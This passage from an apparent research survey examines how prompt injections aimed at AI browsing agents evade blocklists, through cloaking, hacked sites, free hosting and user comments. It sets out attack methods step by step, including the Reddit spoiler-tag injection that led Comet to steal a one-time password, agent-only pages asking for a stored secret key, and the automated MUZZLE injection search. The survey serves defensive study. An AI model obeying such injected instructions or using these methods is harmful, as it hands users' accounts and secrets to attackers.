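*From Past to Present* (2025), a survey of ways to detect malicious addresses, still describes anti-phishing systems as vulnerable to both kinds of cloaking. *PhishLang* reports that in late 2023, blocklists covered evasive phishing pages less well than other phishing pages.

If 31% of malicious pages use cloaking, as in the CrawlPhish data, and all of them escape detection, a blocklist that catches 93% of the remaining pages would catch only about 64% of all malicious pages.

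### Why agents may be easier to recognise than people

An attacker who wants to target agents has to recognise them first. Zychlinski (2025), in *A Whole New World*, argues that this is fairly easy because agents are uniform. People's browsers, screens and fonts vary widely, whereas every copy of an agent may run the same software with the same settings. Automation tools can also leave traces in the browser, and some companies publish the details that identify their agents. An agent that runs on a company's servers also has a data-centre IP address, which few human visitors have.

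Agents that run on the user's own computer are harder to detect. They often use an ordinary Chromium browser and the user's home connection, so neither the user agent string nor the network address identifies them. A site can still identify them by their behaviour. *FP-Agent* (Wang, Shafiq and Vekaria, 2026) tested seven agents, including Comet, Atlas and Claude for Chrome, on booking flights, shopping and using a forum on a test site. Each agent completed about 1,000 runs, and 56 students did the same tasks. Some agents pasted text instead of typing it, or jumped straight to a button without moving the mouse across the page.

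A classifier trained on typing, scrolling and mouse movements could tell the agents from the students and from one another. Browser properties alone worked less well, especially for agents that shared a browser. The classifier detected all seven agents, while Cloudflare's commercial bot detection detected one. The test used one site and a known set of agents, so the classifier would probably make more mistakes on the open web. *Whose Agent Are You?* (2026) also identifies agents, from the timing of their traffic and their behaviour in the browser. The stated purpose is to help sites deal with unauthorised scraping, but an attacker could use the same signals.

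An attacker who identifies agents by their behaviour can do so only after they have started to use the page. The attacker would have to add the injected text after that, and would miss an agent that read the page once and left.

However, the attack can still work if the attacker misidentifies many visitors. Showing the injected text to a person does no harm to the attack if the text is invisible, and missing an agent loses one possible victim. Showing the text to a scanner is the serious mistake, so a cautious attacker would show it only to visitors that are clearly agents.

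Server-side phishing sites usually turn away known scanners and show the attack to everyone else, so a scanner with an unfamiliar address can see it. In Zychlinski's design, the server instead shows the harmless page to every visitor it can't identify as an agent, so a new scanner would find nothing unless it looked like one.

Phishers' interactive checks would also work poorly for prompt injection. A script that waits for natural mouse movement would hide the injection from an agent that jumps between buttons. An attacker would instead have to look for the signs of automation that phishers use to keep crawlers out.

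### Demonstrations of agent-only pages

Zychlinski tested the idea on an internal website with a page of software documentation. The server showed people the documentation, but when it recognised an agent, it sent a page that required a secret key stored on the user's computer for authentication. The attack worked against Cursor, a coding tool, with all three models tested: Claude 4 Sonnet, GPT-5 Fast and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

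The experiment shows that the two steps can work together, but gives little idea of how often they would. Zychlinski does not report the number of attempts or any errors in recognising agents, and does not test whether a security company's scanner would have found the page. The models are from 2025, and newer ones may refuse such a request. A coding tool can read secrets that a browser-only agent can't.

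Zychlinski reports no attack of this kind on the live web, and Khodayari and colleagues say their data could not reveal one. Attackers do use some of the techniques involved. Unit 42 found delayed instructions, which can get past some scanners but don't single out agents.

Only someone who controls the server or a script on the page can cloak an injection. A seller who puts an injection in a marketplace listing for a vacuum cleaner normally can't choose which visitors see it. Cloaking therefore weakens blocklists most against sites that attackers own, where blocklists would otherwise work best.

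### What the web scans could have missed

Common Crawl's crawler identifies itself, so a site can easily recognise it and send it a harmless page. The scans of its archive therefore count only injections that sites served to a known crawler.

Scanners probably miss some kinds of injection more often than others. A photographer who objects to AI training wants crawlers to see the notice, and a prankster has little reason to hide a joke from them, but a thief has a reason to hide an attack. The scans may therefore understate the malicious share of injections as well as the total.

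The effect would have to be large to change the overall mix of injections. Destructive commands and attempts to steal data made up about 1% of Khodayari and colleagues' set. If the crawler had seen only a third of these but all of the other injections, their true share would be about 3%. Most injections would still be pranks and protests, but a blocklist built from the scan would cover only a third of the attacks it was meant to stop.

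In the same study, 34% of the HTML injections (1,583 on 1,243 pages) had disappeared by January 2026, which looks like evidence of cloaking. The researchers note that the owners might have changed the pages, or the sites might have sent different content to an automated browser. They reloaded the pages in a visible browser and checked them by hand.

That check helps with sites that hide text from automated browsers, but a person using a normal browser still doesn't look like an AI agent. The missing text is also weak evidence of attacks on agents, because a crawler or scanner had seen all of it a few months earlier. A site that showed injections only to agents would never have entered the data. If some of the 1,583 cases involve selective display, the sites more likely show the text to crawlers and hide it from browsers, which would make sense for a protest against scraping.

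The missing injections came from only 95 hosts, an average of 17 each, so changes to a few sites could account for many of them. But if some were still being shown to other visitors, injections last longer than the 34% disappearance rate suggests.

### Scanning as an agent

The most direct way to counter this is to scan with the agent's own software. PhishParrot does something similar for phishing. It uses a language model to choose a visitor profile that a cloaked site is likely to accept. A company that makes an agent has an easier job because it can run the real product from the same servers that its customers' agents use, so the scanner would look to the site like any other customer's agent.

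This works less well for agents on users' own computers, since a scanner in a data centre has a different kind of IP address. Some sites also vary what they show at random. If a page displayed an injection on one visit in ten, ten scans would have only a 65% chance of finding it, although the attacker would also miss nine in ten agent visits.

Scanning time is a bigger obstacle. Khodayari and colleagues waited 30 seconds for each page to finish loading in a browser. At that rate, 1,000 machines would need almost 14 months to load the 1.2 billion addresses in their Common Crawl search, not counting the time a model would need to read the pages. A company would have to choose which pages to scan, perhaps starting with unfamiliar domains that its customers' agents had recently visited.

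New systems for identifying agents could complicate scanning further. Web Bot Auth, which Wang and colleagues describe, lets an agent sign its requests cryptographically so that sites can verify who sent them. An honest shop could use the signature to admit some agents and refuse others, but an attacker could also use it to recognise an agent reliably. An independent security company couldn't forge the signature to see the same page, so only the agent's maker, or someone it trusted with a key, could do the scan.

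Zychlinski suggests the opposite approach of having agents vary their browser properties to blend in with people. A site that couldn't tell agents from people would have to show the injection to everyone or to nobody. Wang and colleagues found that behaviour reveals agents even when browser properties don't, so changing those properties may not be enough. Sites with legitimate reasons to recognise agents would also find it harder to do so.

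### Reports from agents and comparisons between visits

Cloaking can't hide an injection from a deployed agent, because the attacker wants the agent to see it. But it makes it difficult to convince a blocklist operator that the page is malicious. An operator who checks the reported address with an ordinary crawler may get the harmless page and dismiss the complaint.

In one PhishTime test, Google was far more likely to blocklist a page when the report included evidence such as a screenshot. The pages were visible only to visitors from the United States, and cloaking blocked 47.5% fewer of the crawlers' requests after reports with evidence. An agent's report might likewise work better if it included the text the agent received, the time, and the type of browser.

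Such a report could contain private information if the page was an inbox or an account. *Client-Side Zero-Shot LLM Inference for Comprehensive In-Browser URL Analysis* (2025) proposes analysing pages inside the user's browser, so they aren't sent elsewhere. This protects the current user, but other users benefit only if the browser shares at least the address and the verdict. Reports can also be false. Oest and colleagues argue that evidence makes fakes easier to spot, but a rival could invent a paragraph of injected text in seconds. An operator could wait for matching reports from several unrelated users, though this would lengthen the delay.

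A scanner can also expose cloaking by opening a page once as an agent and once as an ordinary browser, then looking for text that appears only in the agent's copy. This method doesn't need a list of known phrases, so it could catch injections with new wording.

Many harmless pages would differ too, because shops change prices and recommendations, advertisements rotate, and some sites block AI visitors or charge them for access. A blocklist that treated every difference as an attack would soon include much of the web. The comparison is more useful for selecting passages for a model or a person to read, particularly if the extra text contains a request to pay, reveal something or go elsewhere. It also fails when the site doesn't recognise either visitor as an agent, because it then serves both the same harmless page.

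## Compromised legitimate sites and third-party content

An attacker can break into a site that already has a good reputation instead of building one for a new domain. The attacker then benefits from the site's age, links from other sites, search ranking and clean record. An attacker who controls the server can also use cloaking, just as on a site they own. Cofense, an email security company, says that criminals who spread malware this way avoid hosting costs and are harder to trace, and that owners are less likely to scan the files on their sites.

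AI has reduced the effort needed to break into legitimate sites. *Hackers are mass-exploiting two WordPress vulnerabilities* (Constantin, 2026) describes a July attack on WordPress, software that runs a large share of the world's websites. AI helped find and exploit the flaw, and millions of sites may have been vulnerable. *The summer AI started finding holes in WordPress* (Andersen, 2026) puts the cost of searching for such flaws at $25.

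An attacker who hacks a site with a good record benefits from its reputation score. Suppose again that one in 500 of the unfamiliar domains an agent visits is malicious, and that malicious domains are a tenth as likely as harmless ones to be over ten years old and a tenth as likely to have many links from established sites. The odds that a domain with both features is malicious are 1/499 × 1/10 × 1/10, or about one in 50,000. That may be right for old, well-linked domains in general, but a shop's website with both features would get the same score even if it had been hacked that morning.

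A high search rank helps attackers more with prompt injection than with phishing, because agents have to find the page on their own. The fake Python documentation depended on search terms to be found, but an attacker who compromises an established review site has its existing readers from the first day.

### How much abuse is on compromised sites

De Silva, Nabeel and colleagues (2021) report the highest figures in *Compromised or attacker-owned*, a study of over 800 million VirusTotal scans from August to November 2019. Just over half of the malicious websites were on domains under a single owner's control. Of these, 65.6% were on compromised domains and 34.4% were on domains that attackers had registered. The rest were on shared services such as web hosts, and about a fifth of those were also compromised. Overall, compromised sites made up about 44% of the malicious websites, and sites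 on attackers' own domains made up 18%.

Compromised sites make up a smaller share when domains are counted. Interisle's *Phishing Landscape 2025* (2025) classed 77% of phishing domains as malicious registrations, and *Phishing Landscape 2026* (Strutt and Piscitello, 2026) puts that figure at about three quarters for recent years. Quarterly figures in the Cybercrime Information Center's *Phishing Activity* (2026) vary more. *A Longitudinal Study of Recently Observed Malicious Domains* (Mashood and Nabeel, 2026) examined 1.52 million domains that at least five VirusTotal engines had flagged, and classed only 10.7% as compromised.

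| Source | Period | Unit counted | Compromised |
|---|---|---|---|
| de Silva and colleagues | August–November 2019 | Malicious websites | about 44% |
| Lim and colleagues | July 2021–October 2024 | Phishing domains | 34% |
| Interisle | 2025 report | Phishing domains | 23% |
| Cybercrime Information Center | November 2025–January 2026 | Phishing domains | 36% |
| Cybercrime Information Center | February–April 2026 | Phishing domains | 20% |
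| Mashood and Nabeel | January–May 2026 | Malicious domains | 11% |

Part of the gap comes from counting domains. Criminals buy them in bulk and soon discard them, which inflates the count. Mashood and Nabeel found that 78% of attacker-created domains belonged to batches of at least five registered on the same day with the same registrar. The largest batch had 2,168 domains. Criminals' habits may also have changed since 2019.

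The sources also define "compromised" differently. Interisle, much like Lim and colleagues, counts every phishing domain it doesn't judge malicious as compromised, which probably overstates the share. The table applies the same rule to the quarterly figures. Mashood and Nabeel count a domain as compromised only if it was at least three years old when first flagged or was among the 500,000 most popular domains. Their rule would usually count a hacked two-year-old shop as the attacker's own, and would count an old domain that an attacker bought as compromised.

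Only 4,422 of the 1.52 million domains flagged as compromised (0.3%) ranked among the 500,000 most popular. If injections follow the same pattern, agents will seldom visit most hacked sites, though a small shop can still rank well in searches for a particular vacuum cleaner.

### Cleaning a site and getting it off the list

Researchers rarely know when a site was compromised, so they can't easily measure how long it then takes to appear on a blocklist. That is why Lim and colleagues measured their 86-day median from the date of domain registration.

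Cleaning the site can also be slow. NCSC New Zealand's *ClickFix Mitigation* covers attacks in which a hacked site shows visitors a fake prompt, typically telling them to paste a command into their own computer. It advises site owners to reset their WordPress, hosting, database and other passwords, and to inspect theme and plugin files for injected scripts. Andersen found malicious code at line 2002 of a file that comes with every copy of WordPress, which developers normally have no reason to open. In August 2026, attackers used a poisoned data feed to create backdoors in WordPress sites without changing any plugin files (Mascellino, *WordPress Plugins Compromised Without a Single File Change*, 2026), so an owner who compared those files with clean copies would have found no difference.

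An injected sentence may be harder to find than malicious code. Scanners can look for code that doesn't belong on a shop's pages, but an instruction in plain English resembles a product description. The intruder can also store the instruction in the site's database, where a search of theme and plugin files won't find it.

Once the site is clean, the blocklist operator has to remove it from the list. The best evidence on this is *Indicator of Benignity* (Liu, Sun and colleagues, 2026), a study of complaints from 2019 to 2024 about domains that a large security vendor was blocking. The vendor accepted 121,073 of 123,491 complaints. About 10% of complaints came within a week of the domain's detection, 23% within 30 days and half within 120 days.

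Most complaints about the vendor's own detections concerned its detectors for malicious websites, and most of the domains involved belonged to small businesses. Many had been hacked when the vendor detected them but were clean by the time someone complained. Exempting popular sites would not have solved the problem, because even several popularity lists combined included only about 38% of the domains.

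The 120-day figure is a rough guide to how long a cleaned site might stay blocked. It includes sites blocked by mistake as well as cleaned ones, counts only the time until someone complained, and leaves out domains that nobody complained about.

Delisting could take longer for an agent's blocklist because users may not know to complain. People who reach a block page know something is wrong, but an agent that can't open one shop may just recommend another, and the user may never learn that the first exists. The operator would therefore have to recheck entries without waiting for complaints, but a cloaked site could show the scanner a clean page while the injection was still there.

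### The cost of blocking a shop

Blocking a hacked shop's site prevents every agent that uses the list from reading its catalogue, delivery times and returns policy. Liu and colleagues found that blocks, mostly of compromised websites, stopped some firewall users from sending email or making internet calls. Wrongful blocks also occasionally caused financial losses for the firewall vendor's customers.

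Specialists therefore recommend treating attackers' own domains differently from compromised ones. De Silva and colleagues suggest blocking attackers' domains permanently and compromised ones only temporarily. The DNS Abuse Institute's *Compromised Sites and Malicious Registrations* advises registrars, the companies that sell domain names, to suspend malicious registrations but to limit the harm to owners and visitors when a site is compromised. SIDN Labs' *Applying the COMAR classifier to 35k unique phishing URLs* leaves it to the webmaster or hosting provider to remove the content and repair the software on a compromised site. COMAR is a program that distinguishes the two kinds of domain, with 95% accuracy according to Lim and colleagues.

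Liu and colleagues' tool could help identify innocent owners. It uses a language model to search the web for trustworthy evidence that a domain is legitimate, tracing each claim back to a government source. The team ran it on 15 million hostnames that the vendor had flagged over two months in 2025. It found evidence for 6,571, of which 4,338 were the vendor's false positives, 2,051 were compromised and 182 were the tool's own mistakes. It would not help many small shops, because their legitimacy can't be traced to a government website, even indirectly.

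Blocking a single path loses the shop fewer agent visits than blocking its whole domain, but whether it works depends on what the intruder changed. Suppose a shop receives 1,000 agent visits a day, ten of them to one vacuum cleaner page. A blocklist adds an entry on the day of the break-in, the owner removes the injection after ten days, and the entry remains for 120 days.

| Entry | Injection on one product page | Injection in the footer of every page |
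|---|---|---|
| Whole domain | Blocks all 100 harmful visits and 119,900 harmless ones | Blocks all 10,000 harmful visits and 110,000 harmless ones |
| One product page | Blocks all 100 harmful visits and 1,100 harmless ones | Blocks 100 of 10,000 harmful visits and 1,100 harmless ones |

An injection in a site's footer is a realistic case. NCSC New Zealand tells site owners to pay particular attention to a theme's header and footer files, which WordPress normally adds to every page. A blocklist entry for a single path is almost useless against an injection in those files, because the injection would also appear on the site's other pages.

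If the blocklist operator removed the domain entry on the day the owner cleaned the shop's site, the number of harmless visits blocked would fall from 119,900 to 9,900 in the first case and from 110,000 to zero in the second.

On hacked sites, too, blocklist entries for single pages work better against phishing than against prompt injection. A phisher who breaks into a shop's site usually adds a fake login page at a new address. The shop's customers have no reason to visit that address, so blocking it doesn't harm the shop. An injection is most useful to an attacker on the pages that agents already read, and blocking those pages would harm the shop most.

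### Advertisements, frames and scripts from other domains

A blocklist can also help against injections in third-party content if the browser has to fetch that content from a separate address.

Frames are the easiest case because the browser can leave a frame empty if its domain is on the blocklist. Many advertisements arrive in frames, but the domain often belongs to an advertising network with thousands of honest customers, so the filter must either block the whole network or let the malicious advertisement through. Blocking the network is still much less disruptive than blocking a shop, because an agent comparing vacuum cleaners doesn't need the advertisements, though the site's owner may lose income.

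In Google's design for Chrome, Parker explains, the model doesn't see the content of a frame from a site that isn't relevant to the task. This would keep out an injection in a framed advertisement even on the day it first appeared, because nobody has to detect the advertisement first. A frame from a relevant site would still reach the model. The simpler first version tracked only the sites on which the agent could both read and act, so it may not have hidden frames from irrelevant sites.

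A filter has to stop a malicious script before it runs, because any text the script adds becomes part of the page. *Over 1 million WordPress sites at risk after popular plugins hacked* (Fadilpašić, 2026) describes a June 2026 attack in which three popular WordPress plugins served malicious scripts through a compromised content delivery network, a set of servers that distributes files for many websites. Blocking the address that supplied the scripts could have protected visitors to all the affected sites while keeping the sites available. But a delivery network that has served harmless files for years would have a good reputation when an attack begins, and blocking it could also disable the plugins' normal features.

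To show a chat widget, a shop's page often loads a script from the chat company, which opens a frame for the conversation. If an attacker compromised the chat company, a blocklist could remove the widget and leave the shop usable.

Checking embedded addresses doesn't help when the site's own server collects the outside text. A shop might import product descriptions from a supplier and insert them into its pages. The agent's browser contacts only the shop, so the filter never checks the supplier's domain. The same is true of a script that the site copies to its own server. Unit 42 found an injection in a JavaScript file that a site hosted itself, so a check for bad outside domains would have missed it. The file contained instructions for AI agents to buy a subscription.

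Whether the model receives a frame's contents also depends on how the harness reads the page. If the harness extracts text only from the main document, the model may never receive them. If it takes a screenshot, the model receives whatever the frame displays alongside the shop's own text, so the filter has to block the frame before the screenshot.

### Few documented cases of injection

The figures for compromised sites come from phishing and malware. There is much less evidence that intruders plant instructions for AI agents. Unit 42 doesn't describe any of the sites in its 12 detailed cases as hacked, and the two campaigns that Zscaler found used sites the attackers had set up themselves. Khodayari and colleagues' data can't show how many injections came from break-ins.

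According to Help Net Security, Forcepoint found the same injection templates on several domains, and its researchers took this as a sign of organised tools. One intruder could have altered all of those sites, but one person could also own them, or their owners could have copied the text from each other.

The closest documented case involving advertisements is the scam page for military-style glasses, which targeted an AI ad reviewer, not a shopping agent. If the attack had worked, a fraudulent advertisement could have appeared on reputable sites, but it wouldn't necessarily have contained an injection. Parker says that Google's automated testing gives priority to attacks through advertisements and social media posts because they can reach many people, but doesn't report any real attack through an advertisement.

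The phishing pattern may only partly carry over to prompt injection. An intruder who controls a shop's server can steal card numbers at the checkout without relying on a model to make a mistake. Where agents resist most injections, planting one may be a poor use of a break-in. But a hidden sentence takes almost no effort to add and needn't interfere with other crimes. Attackers already put instructions for human visitors on hacked sites in ClickFix attacks, and they could easily add a version for agents.

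## Free hosting and user posts on trusted domains

Attackers can publish on a reputable domain without breaking into it if it accepts content from strangers. Free hosting services let anyone put pages on a subdomain of the service's domain, such as `vacuum-deals.freehost.example`. The attacker controls everything on that subdomain, so a blocklist can include it without affecting the service's other customers. Forums, marketplaces and code-sharing sites give strangers much less control, often letting them add only a comment to a page that other people wrote. A domain blocklist can't block that comment separately from the rest of the page.

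### Phishing on free website builders

In *Phishing in the Free Waters*, Saha Roy, Unique and Nilizadeh (2023) studied phishing sites made with free website builders, which combine hosting with ready-made page designs. They used a system called FreePhish to monitor links on Twitter and Facebook for six months in 2022 and 2023, and found more than 31,400 phishing addresses on 17 services. They compared these with self-hosted phishing sites, which don't use such a service.

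| | On free website builders | Self-hosted |
|---|---|---|
| Listed by Safe Browsing | 18.4% | 74.2% |
| Median delay for listed pages | 6 hours | 51 minutes |
| Median age of the domain | 13.7 years | 71 days |

The 18.4% matches Lee and colleagues' figure for Safe Browsing only by coincidence, since the two studies used different data.

For free-hosted pages, low coverage lets through more visits than the delay does. If each page stayed up for 21 hours with steady traffic, these figures imply that Safe Browsing prevented about 71% of visits to the self-hosted pages and 13% of visits to the free-hosted ones. Cutting the delay for free-hosted pages to 51 minutes would raise the 13% only to 18%.

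Every address in the study came from a social media post. Blocklists might catch even fewer injection pages on the same services, since attackers don't have to advertise those pages.

### Why free hosting hides a site from blocklists

Certificates explain part of the gap. A new domain shows up in the certificate logs that security companies watch, but a hosting service typically uses one certificate for all its subdomains, so a new page on the service adds nothing to the logs.

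This also limits what later studies can show. *PhishLang* scanned 42.7 million domains between September 2023 and January 2024, all taken from certificate logs. Safe Browsing had already listed 51% of the regular phishing sites in the study's test. That is far above 18.4%, but the scan would have missed most pages that share a certificate, so the difference isn't evidence that Safe Browsing had improved on free hosting.

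Domain age is misleading too. A subdomain has no registration date of its own, so a reputation score may use the hosting service's age even for a page created this morning. A security company could instead use the date it first saw the subdomain, but that would help only a little because harmless new sites appear on these services all the time.

Strutt and Piscitello write that businesses implicitly trust any address under domains such as pages.dev and windows.net. An agent's developer could make the same mistake by exempting well-known hosting domains from the blocklist check. Strutt and Piscitello also write that some providers offer AI tools that can produce near-copies of a company's pages, and that providers struggle to find disguised scripts quickly.

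The certificate and age problems apply equally to pages with injections, and a few of the sites Unit 42 listed were already on such services.

### How much phishing uses free hosting

The consulting firm Interisle counts phishing attacks hosted on what it calls subdomain providers, which include free and cheap hosting services. It publishes much of this data through the Cybercrime Information Center. The years below run from May to April.

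| Period | All phishing attacks | On subdomain providers | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2022–23 | over 1.8 million | not given | over 16% |
| 2023–24 | not given | over 450,000 | 24% |
| 2024–25 | 1,963,390 | 202,585 or 256,026 | 10% or 13% |
| 2025–26 | 4,251,720 | 432,990 | 10% |
| May–July 2026 | 1,450,117 | 102,947 | 7% |

The 24% comes from Interisle's *Phishing Landscape 2024* (2024). Interisle first published the higher count for the following year, and a later comparison by the Cybercrime Information Center has the lower one. By the lower count, attacks on these services more than doubled in 2025–26, but their share of all phishing stayed the same because phishing as a whole also more than doubled. In the Cybercrime Information Center's most recent quarter, the number of attacks rose slightly and their share fell.

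Strutt and Piscitello attribute most of the earlier drop to a decline in phishing on Google's Blogspot, and the recent growth to other providers. These figures count attacks, so they don't show whether blocklists now catch more of them.

### Blocking one subdomain or the whole service

A blocklist entry for one subdomain blocks only the attacker's site, but the attacker can replace that site for free by opening a new account.

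Blocking the whole service would stop the replacements. According to Interisle, eight providers hosted 80% of the phishing attacks that used subdomain providers in 2022–23. Blocking all eight would therefore have covered about 13% of all phishing attacks that year. It would also have blocked every harmless site on those services. Several of the services are meant for developers, so a coding agent would lose some of the pages it most needs.

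The same concentration makes the hosting companies well placed to act, because each can delete an attacker's site and close the account. When Saha Roy and colleagues reported the phishing sites that FreePhish found, some services removed them, but others were slow or left them up. In the *PhishLang* test, the share of regular phishing sites that were offline rose from 39% before the researchers reported the rest to 61% afterwards.

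### A Reddit comment that gave away an account

In August 2025, Chaikin and Sahib, in *Agentic Browser Security*, showed how a single Reddit comment could let an attacker take over a user's Perplexity account. Both work for Brave, which makes a competing browser. The comment contained instructions behind a spoiler tag, which hides text until a reader clicks on it. When a user of Perplexity's Comet browser opened the thread and asked for a summary, the model received the hidden text along with everything else. Comet then did the following:

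1. It opened the user's Perplexity account page and copied the email address.
2. It started a new login with that address, so Perplexity emailed the user a one-time password.
3. It opened Gmail, where the user was already logged in, and read the password.
4. It posted the email address and the password as a reply to the Reddit comment.

The attacker needed only to read the reply. The user did nothing after asking for the summary.

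Checking a blocklist before every page load would not have stopped this attack on Comet, because the agent visited only Reddit, Perplexity and Gmail. The instructions had it log in at `perplexity.ai.`, with a dot at the end, which the browser treated as a different domain, so the user's existing login didn't apply. Safe Browsing's rules remove that dot before the lookup, so the filter would have checked Perplexity's ordinary address. The attacker didn't need a server to collect the stolen data, since Comet posted it on Reddit.

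Chaikin and Sahib showed that the attack was possible but didn't measure how often it worked. They reported it to Perplexity on 25 July 2025, and Perplexity made a first fix two days later. A retest showed that the fix was incomplete. The attack seemed to have stopped working by 13 August, but further tests after publication on 20 August showed that Perplexity still hadn't fully prevented it.

Willison's *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots* quotes Brave's October 2025 follow-up, which describes the problem as systemic across AI browsers. The follow-up again uses the example of a user asking for a summary of a Reddit post.

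### Tests with ordinary posts and comments

*WASP* (Evtimov, Zharmagambetov and colleagues, 2025) tested such attacks on private copies of the code-sharing site GitLab and a Reddit-like forum. Earlier tests had often let the attacker control the entire page. In WASP, the attacker could write posts, comments and issues (reports of problems in a software project) but couldn't change the page's layout or anyone else's text.

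The team wrote 21 attacker goals, such as deleting the user's project or changing the email address on the user's account, and combined each with two ordinary tasks, such as adding a thumbs-up to an issue. The agents ran on models including GPT-4o, o1 and Claude. The injections diverted them in up to 86% of cases, but the agents completed the attackers' goals much less often. The researchers attribute this to the agents' limited capability, which is not a lasting safeguard.

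Only five of the 21 goals require the agent to open an address on the attacker's domain, usually to deliver stolen information. A blocklist could at best stop those five at the last step. The agent can achieve the other 16 without leaving the trusted site. The researchers chose the goals, so real attackers may use their own domains more or less often.

WASP used fixed, handwritten injections, while *MUZZLE* (Syros, Rose and colleagues, 2026) automates the attacker. Its system monitors an agent doing an ordinary task and ranks the places on each page where a user could add text that the agent would read. It puts a placeholder in the top-ranked place and rewrites the injection until the model's next step departs from the task. Then it runs the whole task again with the injection included. If the attack fails, the system tries other wording or another place.

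The team used private copies of a code-sharing site, a forum, a marketplace and a database tool. These are the results for Browser Use with GPT-4o:

| Where the attack took place | Runs | Agent adopted the attacker's goal | Agent completed it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code-sharing site | 15 | 11 | 3 |
| Forum | 15 | 12 | 7 |
| Marketplace | 15 | 11 | 5 |
| From one site to another | 10 | 9 | 3 |
| Total | 55 | 43 | 18 |

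With two other models and a second agent included, the system achieved 44 complete attacks in 100 runs. Each run allowed repeated attempts to improve the injection, so the 44% figure is not the success rate of a single comment.

Replies and comments were the most effective places to plant injections on the code-sharing site, the forum and the marketplace. New forum posts quickly dropped out of view, whereas a reply appeared in a thread that the agent was about to read. A blocklist entry for that thread would also block the post that the user wanted the agent to read.

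The forum's most successful attack sent the agent to a fake login page presented as a verification step, and it worked in four of five runs with GPT-4o. The attacker hosted that page, so a blocklist could have stopped the agent once the page's address was on the list. In two of five runs, a marketplace reply made the agent delete a table of orders from the separate database without needing such a page.

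Syros and colleagues also compared their injections with WASP's fixed wording. Over 30 runs, theirs completed the attacker's goal 87% of the time, compared with 20% for WASP's. The comparison favours their system because they chose goals it had already achieved. None of the agents had dedicated defences against prompt injection, and the models date from 2024 and 2025.

Newer models do better against the old wording. *Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) repeated part of WASP in July 2026 with GPT-5.4-mini, a small model. The attack succeeded in one of 21 cases with one user task and in none of 21 with the other. But deceptive pop-ups succeeded against the same model in 85.5% of runs, averaged across three kinds. The two rates aren't directly comparable, since a click on the pop-up counted as a success. Still, the results show that a model can resist one well-known injection and remain easy to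 divert with another.

### Posts that have their own address

A blocklist of full addresses can isolate some kinds of user content, depending on how the platform arranges its pages.

| What the attacker wrote | Narrowest entry | What else the entry blocks |
|---|---|---|
| A code repository | The repository's path | Nothing |
| A shared document | The document's URL | Nothing, unless other people contributed |
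| A job advertisement | The advertisement's URL | Nothing, though search results may still show the text |
| An issue or forum post | The thread's URL | Other people's replies |
| A comment or product review | The URL of the whole page | The post or product that the user asked about |

Blocking individual paths works well for repositories. The attacker behind the fake Python documentation had set up matching repositories on GitHub, and blocking their paths would have left the rest of GitHub available. The attacker could upload the same files under a new name within minutes, but the new repository would start with no links or visitors.

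Malicious comments are much harder to block by listing pages, because an attacker can paste the same comment into many threads. A company trying to list every affected thread would also have to find each one while agents were still reading it, and a busy discussion may be read for only a few hours.

### What platforms can remove

The platform's moderators can delete one comment without removing the thread. The platform also has better information than any outside scanner, because it receives the text before any agent does and knows the account's age and posting history. It can remove every copy at once. The poster normally can't use cloaking to show the platform different text from what agents see.

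Moderators rely partly on reports from users, who are unlikely to report text they can't see. An automated check could read everything, including text behind spoiler tags. On GitHub, however, it would have trouble telling real attacks from the examples that security researchers post, as every detector does with articles about prompt injection. Job boards have a different problem, because the employers who set traps for automated applications are their paying customers.

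Platforms don't always act on ordinary fraud, even after someone reports it. Saha Roy and colleagues found that Twitter and Facebook, like some of the hosting services, were slow to remove phishing posts or didn't remove them at all. Those posts contained links that anyone could open and check. Platforms may take longer to remove a prompt injection, which can look like just a strange sentence and harms only other people's agents.

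Public moderation also doesn't cover shared documents and private messages. An email provider can scan messages for injections as it does for spam, but no moderator reads them and no other user can report them. Google Docs and email were among the services Comet users most often asked their agent to work on.

### Marking users' text as untrusted

The agent's own software can also treat text differently depending on who wrote it, without the platform's cooperation. Villa and Tan's system, Prismata, runs between the browser and the agent and makes two checks on each page.

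One check uses a language model to decide whether the user's task requires a given button, link or form field. The model receives only the task, the item and the page elements that contain it, so a malicious comment elsewhere on the page can't influence the decision.

The other check labels each region of the page by its source: the site's developer, users, sellers or outside parties such as advertisers. The labelling model works down from the top of the page's structure. When it reaches a heading such as "Customer reviews", it can label everything under that heading as users' text without processing the text itself.

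Ordinary code then enforces the decisions by removing regions the task doesn't need and making the remaining untrusted ones read-only. An agent told to buy the best-reviewed vacuum cleaner could still read the reviews, but it couldn't click on anything inside them. It also couldn't open the account settings, because the purchase doesn't require them.

This depends on sites labelling their users' text clearly. Villa and Tan tested that on 5,664 pages from popular sites and recorded browsing tasks, with language models doing most of the annotation. They found 90,408 pieces of content from outsiders, and 1,086 of them (1.2%) contained an element an agent could click or fill in. In all but 94 of those cases, a heading or another cue came before that element.

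In the pop-up tests, Prismata reduced the attack success rate from 85.5% to 0.7%. On pages without attacks, the agent completed 26.6% of its tasks with Prismata and 29.9% without it, or about one-ninth fewer. Blocking a platform's domain would prevent the agent from completing any task that depends on that platform.

Prismata works on text but not on screenshots. It also can't stop an attack that stays within the user's task, so a fake review could still persuade the agent to buy the wrong vacuum cleaner. Villa and Tan leave fake reviews to platforms' moderators, who were dealing with them long before agents existed. This gap is significant because promotion was far more common than theft or destructive commands among the injections Khodayari and colleagues found.

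The system also depends on the site itself being trustworthy. Someone who owns a site, or has broken into one, could present an injection as the developer's own text. A blocklist is most useful against sites that attackers own, so the two defences cover different sources of injection, and an agent could use both.

### What an agent would lose without Reddit or GitHub

A developer could decide that a platform is too risky and block it entirely. Whether that makes sense depends on four quantities: the share of the platform's pages with a harmful injection (p), the attack success rate (s), the damage from a successful attack (D) and the value to the user of reading one page (V). Blocking is worthwhile if:

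p × s × D > V

Blocking whole platforms becomes harder to justify as models get better at resisting injected orders. If one Reddit thread in 10,000 contained an order to send $5,000, and the agent obeyed such orders 1% of the time, the expected loss would be half a cent per thread. Most people would accept that to find out whether a vacuum cleaner breaks after a year. If the agent obeyed half the time, the expected loss would be 25 cents per thread, and blocking Reddit would be much easier to defend. The one in 10,000 is invented, and the web scans don't provide a real figure for Reddit.

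The calculation also overstates the benefit of the block, because it assumes that the agent reads nothing instead. An agent that couldn't open Reddit would probably look for owners' opinions in another forum or in a shop's reviews, which are also written by strangers.

A coding agent often has no substitute for GitHub. The site may host the user's own project, including issues filed by strangers that the user wants the agent to answer. Many of the tasks in WASP and MUZZLE were of this kind, so blocking the site would stop the task as well as the attack. A shopping agent could easily do without GitHub, but it would rarely visit the site, so a block would remove little exposure.

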